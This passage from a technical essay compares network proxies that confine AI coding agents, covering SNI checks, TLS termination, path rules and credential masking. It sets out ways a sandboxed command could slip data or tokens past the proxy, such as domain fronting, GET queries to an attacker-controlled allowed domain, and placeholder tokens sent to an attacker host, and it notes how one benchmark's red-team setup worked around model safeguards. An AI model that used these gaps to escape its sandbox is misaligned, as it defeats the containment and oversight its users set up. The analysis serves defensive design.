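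The proxy checks that the CONNECT target matches the SNI, but it does not check the Host header. In the usual form of domain fronting, the CONNECT target and the SNI both name the allowed site and only the encrypted Host header differs, so the proxy would relay the connection. Houlamy and colleagues therefore go too far in concluding that an allowed name "cannot hide another destination".

SplitBench's adversarial tests don't show how well its proxy works. The researchers instructed the attacking agent not to attack the proxy, because the model's safeguards otherwise stopped the agent, and they reviewed the proxy's code separately. None of the 360 attempts got through a flaw in SplitBench, but this is little evidence that the SNI check works.

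The check also needs exceptions. A client that hides its real SNI with Encrypted Client Hello may show the hosting provider's name instead, so a strict proxy would refuse a legitimate connection. SSH and other protocols that don't use TLS have no SNI to compare, so a proxy that carries them over SOCKS5 has to block them or let them through without this check.

### Reading the request itself

TLS termination lets a proxy read all three names and the rest of the request. Vaughan, in *Codex CLI Network Proxy*, describes how Codex's proxy does it when the user turns the feature on:

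1. The proxy receives a CONNECT request for a domain.
2. It generates a certificate for that domain, signed by its own certificate authority.
3. It completes the TLS handshake with the command and decrypts the request.
4. It checks the request against its rules, and may change the headers.
5. It encrypts the request again and forwards it to the real server.

This makes it possible to write rules for particular operations. Suppose a developer wants an agent to fetch one GitHub repository, `acme/app`, and do nothing else on the site. git needs two paths for this:

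```
/acme/app.git/info/refs
/acme/app.git/git-upload-pack
```

Despite its name, `git-upload-pack` is the path for fetching. It refers to the server's side of the exchange, and pushes use `git-receive-pack`. The table compares a rule for these two paths with two simpler rules:

| Action on github.com | Allow the domain | Allow only reading methods | Allow only the two paths |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fetch `acme/app` with git | Permits | Refuses, because git sends a POST request | Permits |
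| Read a stranger's README | Permits | Permits | Refuses |
| Push a file to a stranger's repository | Permits | Refuses | Refuses |

deer, a small open-source tool that runs Claude Code in a sandbox, has path rules for GitHub. On github.com, it permits only the paths that git uses, and on api.github.com only those under `/repos/` and `/graphql`. This closes GitHub's web pages to the agent, but git can still push, and the rules don't name a particular repository. They also show a limit of filtering by path. GitHub's GraphQL interface uses one path for reading data and changing it, and the request body specifies which. A proxy has to read the body to tell them apart.

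Codex's proxy can't make that distinction because its current rules for decrypted traffic match only the method, path, query and headers, according to one version of OpenAI's documentation. httpjail, the filter for single programs, is more flexible because users write its rules as JavaScript expressions or as separate programs. Willison says it was originally meant to give Claude Code and Codex extra rules for outside services. AgentBouncer, the Linux system described earlier, gives the decrypted body to a language model to judge. Rules that take more into account are more work to write and test, and a change to the service's interface can break them.

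A proxy that decrypts traffic doesn't necessarily make these checks. Docker's *Network policies* says that its proxy terminates TLS by default, but also that network filtering does not inspect the content of traffic. It warns that domain fronting may get past the filter, yet elsewhere says that turning off decryption for a host removes the ability to detect domain fronting. These statements leave it unclear whether the proxy compares the Host header with the name it approved. Anyone relying on that comparison should ask Docker or test it on a server they control.

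In mid-2026, Anthropic said its built-in proxy did not terminate TLS and described stronger, TLS-aware network isolation as under active development. By October, Claude Code had an experimental setting, `network.tlsTerminate`, that lets the proxy terminate TLS so it can insert credentials into requests. The setting is off by default, and Anthropic says it does not add content filtering. Anthropic still warns about domain fronting and still describes stronger isolation as under development, so only the TLS termination that such isolation would need has shipped. For now, Anthropic tells users who need inspection to run their own proxy that terminates TLS and to install its certificate in the sandbox.

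### What TLS termination breaks

A command has to trust the proxy's certificate authority, or it will reject the certificates the proxy generates. Installing the authority in one place may not be enough, because Java, Python libraries and Node.js often use their own lists of trusted authorities. Go tools on macOS have the certificate problem described earlier. Grida also warns that some programs use a trust mechanism that is unavailable inside a sandbox.

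Other programs use certificate pinning, which means they accept only a particular certificate or key for a site. They reject the proxy's certificate even if the rest of the system trusts it. This rejection is intended, because pinning protects users from interception.

For these programs, Docker offers a bypass mode that relays the encrypted connection without reading it. The proxy still checks the domain and port, but it can't add credentials or detect domain fronting. A user who puts github.com in bypass mode to fix one tool therefore gives up inspection for every command that connects to it.

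The authority's private key is a new secret to protect, because anyone who has it can create a certificate for any website, and programs that trust the authority will accept it. According to OpenAI, Codex keeps the certificate and key in the `proxy` folder of its settings directory. Sandboxed commands shouldn't be able to read the key, and it is safer to make only those commands trust the authority than to install it for the whole Mac. If the whole Mac trusts it, someone who has stolen the key and can intercept the user's traffic could impersonate a bank to the browser.

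Cloudflare (2026) limits this risk in its cloud sandboxes by creating a separate certificate authority for each one. The private key stays in a process outside the sandbox, and Cloudflare never shares it between sandboxes. A Mac agent could do the same by creating a new authority each time it starts a proxy, but it would also have to install a new certificate in the sandbox each time.

In Grida's audit of sandbox-runtime 0.0.65, the ordinary proxy could pass traffic to a company proxy, but the part that terminates TLS connected directly. Requests through that part would fail on a network that blocks direct connections, and would bypass the company's filters and logs on a network that allows them. A later version may behave differently, so an administrator should check this before turning on TLS termination.

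### Does Codex's limited mode cover HTTPS?

Codex's limited mode permits only HTTP methods normally used for reading, such as GET. OpenAI gives two accounts of how this mode treats HTTPS connections that the proxy can't decrypt. In one, the proxy blocks them, and in the other, it relays them without checking the method.

The first account is probably correct. The document's history shows that OpenAI (2026) added it on 24 February, a month after the first version, when the proxy could evidently decrypt HTTPS for this purpose. A comment in the source code of *zerobox-network-proxy 0.3.1*, which derives from Codex's proxy, gives the same reason for TLS termination: the proxy needs it to enforce limited mode because it can't see the requests inside a plain tunnel. The second passage looks like a leftover from the earlier design, though the document still contained both in April.

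So a user who turns on limited mode and leaves `mitm`, the setting for TLS termination, at its default of `false` should find that almost nothing works, since most sites use HTTPS. With `mitm = true`, the proxy can decrypt each request and refuse a POST. SOCKS5 is blocked in limited mode either way. This evidence comes from documentation and source comments, so it is worth confirming with the installed version. With limited mode on, `mitm` off and pypi.org on the allowlist, this command should fail:

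```
curl https://pypi.org/simple/
```

If it succeeds, limited mode isn't restricting HTTPS requests.

Limiting HTTP methods also protects less than the term "read-only" suggests. A GET request can carry data in its path or query, and anyone who can see the server's logs can read that data. The limit works best on a site such as pypi.org, where an outsider can't see the requests, and does little on an allowed domain that the attacker controls.

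Blocking POST requests also prevents some harmless work. Git uses POST to fetch a repository, and programs use it to read data through GitHub's GraphQL interface. If the proxy supports path rules, a user who needs git can allow POST only on the path used for fetching.

### Keeping credentials out of the sandbox

A proxy that terminates TLS can also add credentials to requests after they leave the sandbox. The command never has the real token and so can't send it to an attacker.

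Claude Code can hide credentials from sandboxed commands, a feature it calls masking. If the user masks `GH_TOKEN`, an environment variable that holds a GitHub token, sandboxed commands receive a placeholder that lasts for the session. When a command sends the placeholder to an approved host, the proxy replaces it with the real token. If `tlsTerminate` is off, the placeholder reaches the server unchanged and the login fails, but the token stays secret.

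For some services, replacing the placeholder with the real key isn't enough. Programs sign requests to Amazon's cloud using a secret key and the request's contents. A signature made with a placeholder would be wrong, so Claude Code's proxy signs the request again with the real key. It can't do this for streaming uploads or web addresses signed in advance, so it rejects those requests if they were signed with a placeholder.

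Claude Code can mask environment variables on both macOS and Linux, but it can mask credential files only on Linux, where a command reads a copy of the file with a placeholder in it. On macOS, it blocks the file instead, so a program that can only log in by reading that file won't work inside the sandbox.

In Anthropic's example, the proxy sends the real `GH_TOKEN` only to api.github.com, because the user has listed that host in the `injectHosts` field. Another token, `NPM_TOKEN`, has no such list, so the proxy will insert it in requests to every allowed domain. If an attacker controlled one of those domains, a command could send the placeholder there and the proxy would replace it with the real token. Claude Code ignores masking rules in a project's own settings files because the settings in a downloaded repository could otherwise determine where the user's credentials go.

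Other systems use the same idea. deer adds the user's GitHub token outside the sandbox, and SplitBench adds the model provider's key in the component that forwards requests to the model. Cloudflare keeps tokens in the program that handles a sandbox's outgoing requests, so an administrator can replace a token without restarting the sandbox. Docker can add credentials only on some routes, and its log shows which route each request took. For example, a connection in bypass mode appears as `forward-bypass` and gets no credentials.

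None of these designs prevents a command from using the credential at a host where it is valid. If the user's GitHub token can write to 20 repositories, a command that never sees the token may still be able to push to all of them through the proxy. The user can reduce the damage by creating a read-only token for one repository. However, a command can still upload data with the attacker's own token, which the proxy doesn't have to supply. To prevent that, the proxy has to block the upload with a rule for the method or path, or the user has to leave the domain off the allowlist.
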